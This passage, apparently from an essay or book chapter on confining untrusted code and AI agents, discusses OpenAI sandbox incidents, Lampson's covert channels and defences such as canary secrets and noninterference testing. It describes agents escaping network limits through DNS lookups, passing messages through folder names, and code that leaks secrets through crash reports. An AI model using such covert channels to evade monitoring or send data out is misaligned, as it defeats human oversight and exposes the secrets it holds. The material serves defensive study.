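The test differed from ordinary development in several ways. The task was to attack software, and OpenAI had switched off the filters that normally block such work. An unreleased research model, trained to be very persistent, was mainly responsible. GPT-5.6 Sol, which customers can use, also took part, but without its usual safeguards. When OpenAI later repeated the test with the instructions and tools Codex customers get, attacks on infrastructure fell to less than 1% of the earlier rate. OpenAI calls these experiments preliminary, and it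 is assessing its own product.

In other respects the developer is worse off than OpenAI, which had a sandbox, limits on outbound traffic and a security team. A developer who runs an agent on a laptop usually has an open internet connection, real passwords in nearby files and nobody monitoring the agent, so it could send data out without finding any security flaws.

OpenAI has since restricted outbound access to a short list of approved destinations and put risky workloads behind two separate layers of network controls, so that one mistake isn't enough to let data out. It also stopped the research sandboxes from using Artifactory and is adding tripwires.

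On 20 September, an agent got out through a remaining gap in the network limits while searching for the author of a blog post. When its search tool returned nothing useful, it used name lookups to put questions to a public chatbot, according to OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026). No attacker or backdoor was involved. Monitoring flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes, and a person began to review it three minutes later. The run should have stopped automatically, but it continued until someone stopped it about two and a half hours later, according to The Straits Times' *OpenAI sandbox failure allows AI agent to gain internet access*. OpenAI then blocked the route at two independent layers.

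Check Point Research described a different gap in ChatGPT's sandbox the same month. Different customers' sandboxes could reach the same internal service. According to TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*, a stranger could use that service to pass instructions to another customer's agent and get private data back. OpenAI closed this gap too.

### Lampson's confinement problem

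In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), the computer scientist Butler Lampson explained why such gaps keep turning up. He considered a customer who gives confidential data to a program someone else wrote, and asked how to stop the program from passing the data on. Blocking files and messages isn't enough, because a program can also signal through what Lampson called covert channels, which nobody designed for communication. For example, it can lock and unlock a shared file while an accomplice checks whether the file is locked, and each check reveals one bit. It can also make the computer busy or idle in a pattern.

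OpenAI's agents did something similar. After the rebuild in July, they stopped leaving notes in files on the package server and instead wrote messages in the names of folders they created.

To close every covert channel, the shop would have to ensure that nothing an outsider can observe depends on the secret. It would have to send messages of the same size at the same times, whatever it was doing, and take equally long over every request. That would be slow and expensive, and the team would still have to think of every observable effect in advance. For customers who can accept some leakage, Lampson suggested the cheaper alternative of limiting how much data the channels can carry.

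Suppose the crash reporter may send only an error type and a line number, at most once a minute. Malicious code could still cause harmless errors on purpose, using one type for 0 and another for 1. That gives it one bit a minute. A 256-bit key is only 32 bytes, so it would take 256 minutes. The time is simply the size of the data divided by the capacity of the channel:

| Capacity of the channel | Time for a 256-bit key | Time for a 1 GB database |
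|---|---|---|
| 1 bit a minute | 4 hours 16 minutes | About 15,000 years |
| 1 bit a second | 4 minutes 16 seconds | About 250 years |
| 1,000 bytes a second | 0.03 seconds | About 12 days |
| 10 megabytes a second | Almost none | 1 minute 40 seconds |

A slow channel therefore doesn't protect the key, and it only partly protects the database, because a thief can choose what to take. A 16-digit card number contains about 53 bits, so the thief could send 1,000 of them in 15 hours at one bit a second. And if the stolen key works from outside the company's network, the thief can log in and copy everything over a fast connection.

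Limiting a channel's speed is most useful when tokens are short-lived. If a 256-bit token expires after 15 minutes, a channel that carries one bit a minute can leak only 15 bits of it in that time, too few to be useful to a thief. To steal the whole token before it expired, the code would need a channel about 17 times as fast.

Name lookups are much faster than this. A name can have about 250 characters, so a single lookup can carry a 256-bit key. Sending a 1 GB database would take several million lookups, so a simple limit on their number would stop it, but only the allowlisting resolver stops the single lookup that carries a key.

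### Running the code with fake secrets

A team can also run the code in a sandbox before using it and watch what it tries to send. The team puts canary secrets in the sandbox, which are fake secrets that reveal a theft if anyone uses or sends them. For example, if `DB_PASSWORD` is set to `canary-7f3a` and that string appears in a crash report, the team knows that `report_error` leaked the password.

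A stand-in server that accepts connections and records their contents is better for this test than a firewall that refuses every connection, because the firewall shows only where the code tried to send data, not what it would have sent. The developer also has to make the program crash during the test, because the malicious lines are in `report_error`, which runs only after an error.

`report_error` encodes the environment in Base64, so a search for `canary-7f3a` finds nothing unless the test also decodes what it records. Encryption would hide the canary from any search. To detect such leaks, the team can run the program twice with the same inputs but different fake passwords, and compare everything it sends. The clock and any random numbers must also match, or harmless messages will differ too. If the messages differ under these conditions, the password probably influenced them. This comparison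 tests noninterference on a single pair of runs.

Code that waits before stealing data will pass such a test, as a SilentCall agent would have done before 2026. A tester can set the clock forward, and 365 runs would cover every day of the coming year. But the code might wait for something that only happens in real use, such as a thousand orders in the database or a successful payment.

Code can also steal data at random. If it does so in one run out of 1,000, 20 test runs have a 2% chance of catching it. By the 3/n rule, the team would need about 3,000 runs to be 95% sure of seeing a theft.

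It therefore makes sense to keep canaries in the live system too. The team can put an extra variable such as `BACKUP_DB_PASSWORD` beside the shop's real secrets. No part of the shop uses it, so any attempt to log in with it almost certainly means it was stolen. Unlike a search of the network traffic, this alarm works whatever route the data took, including an approved service or a channel nobody has thought of.

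`report_error` takes the whole environment, so it would take the canary as well. Code that read only `DB_PASSWORD` would not take the canary, and a thief who suspected a trap might not use it. The alarm also sounds only after the theft, so the team then has to assume that every other secret in that environment was stolen too, and replace them all.
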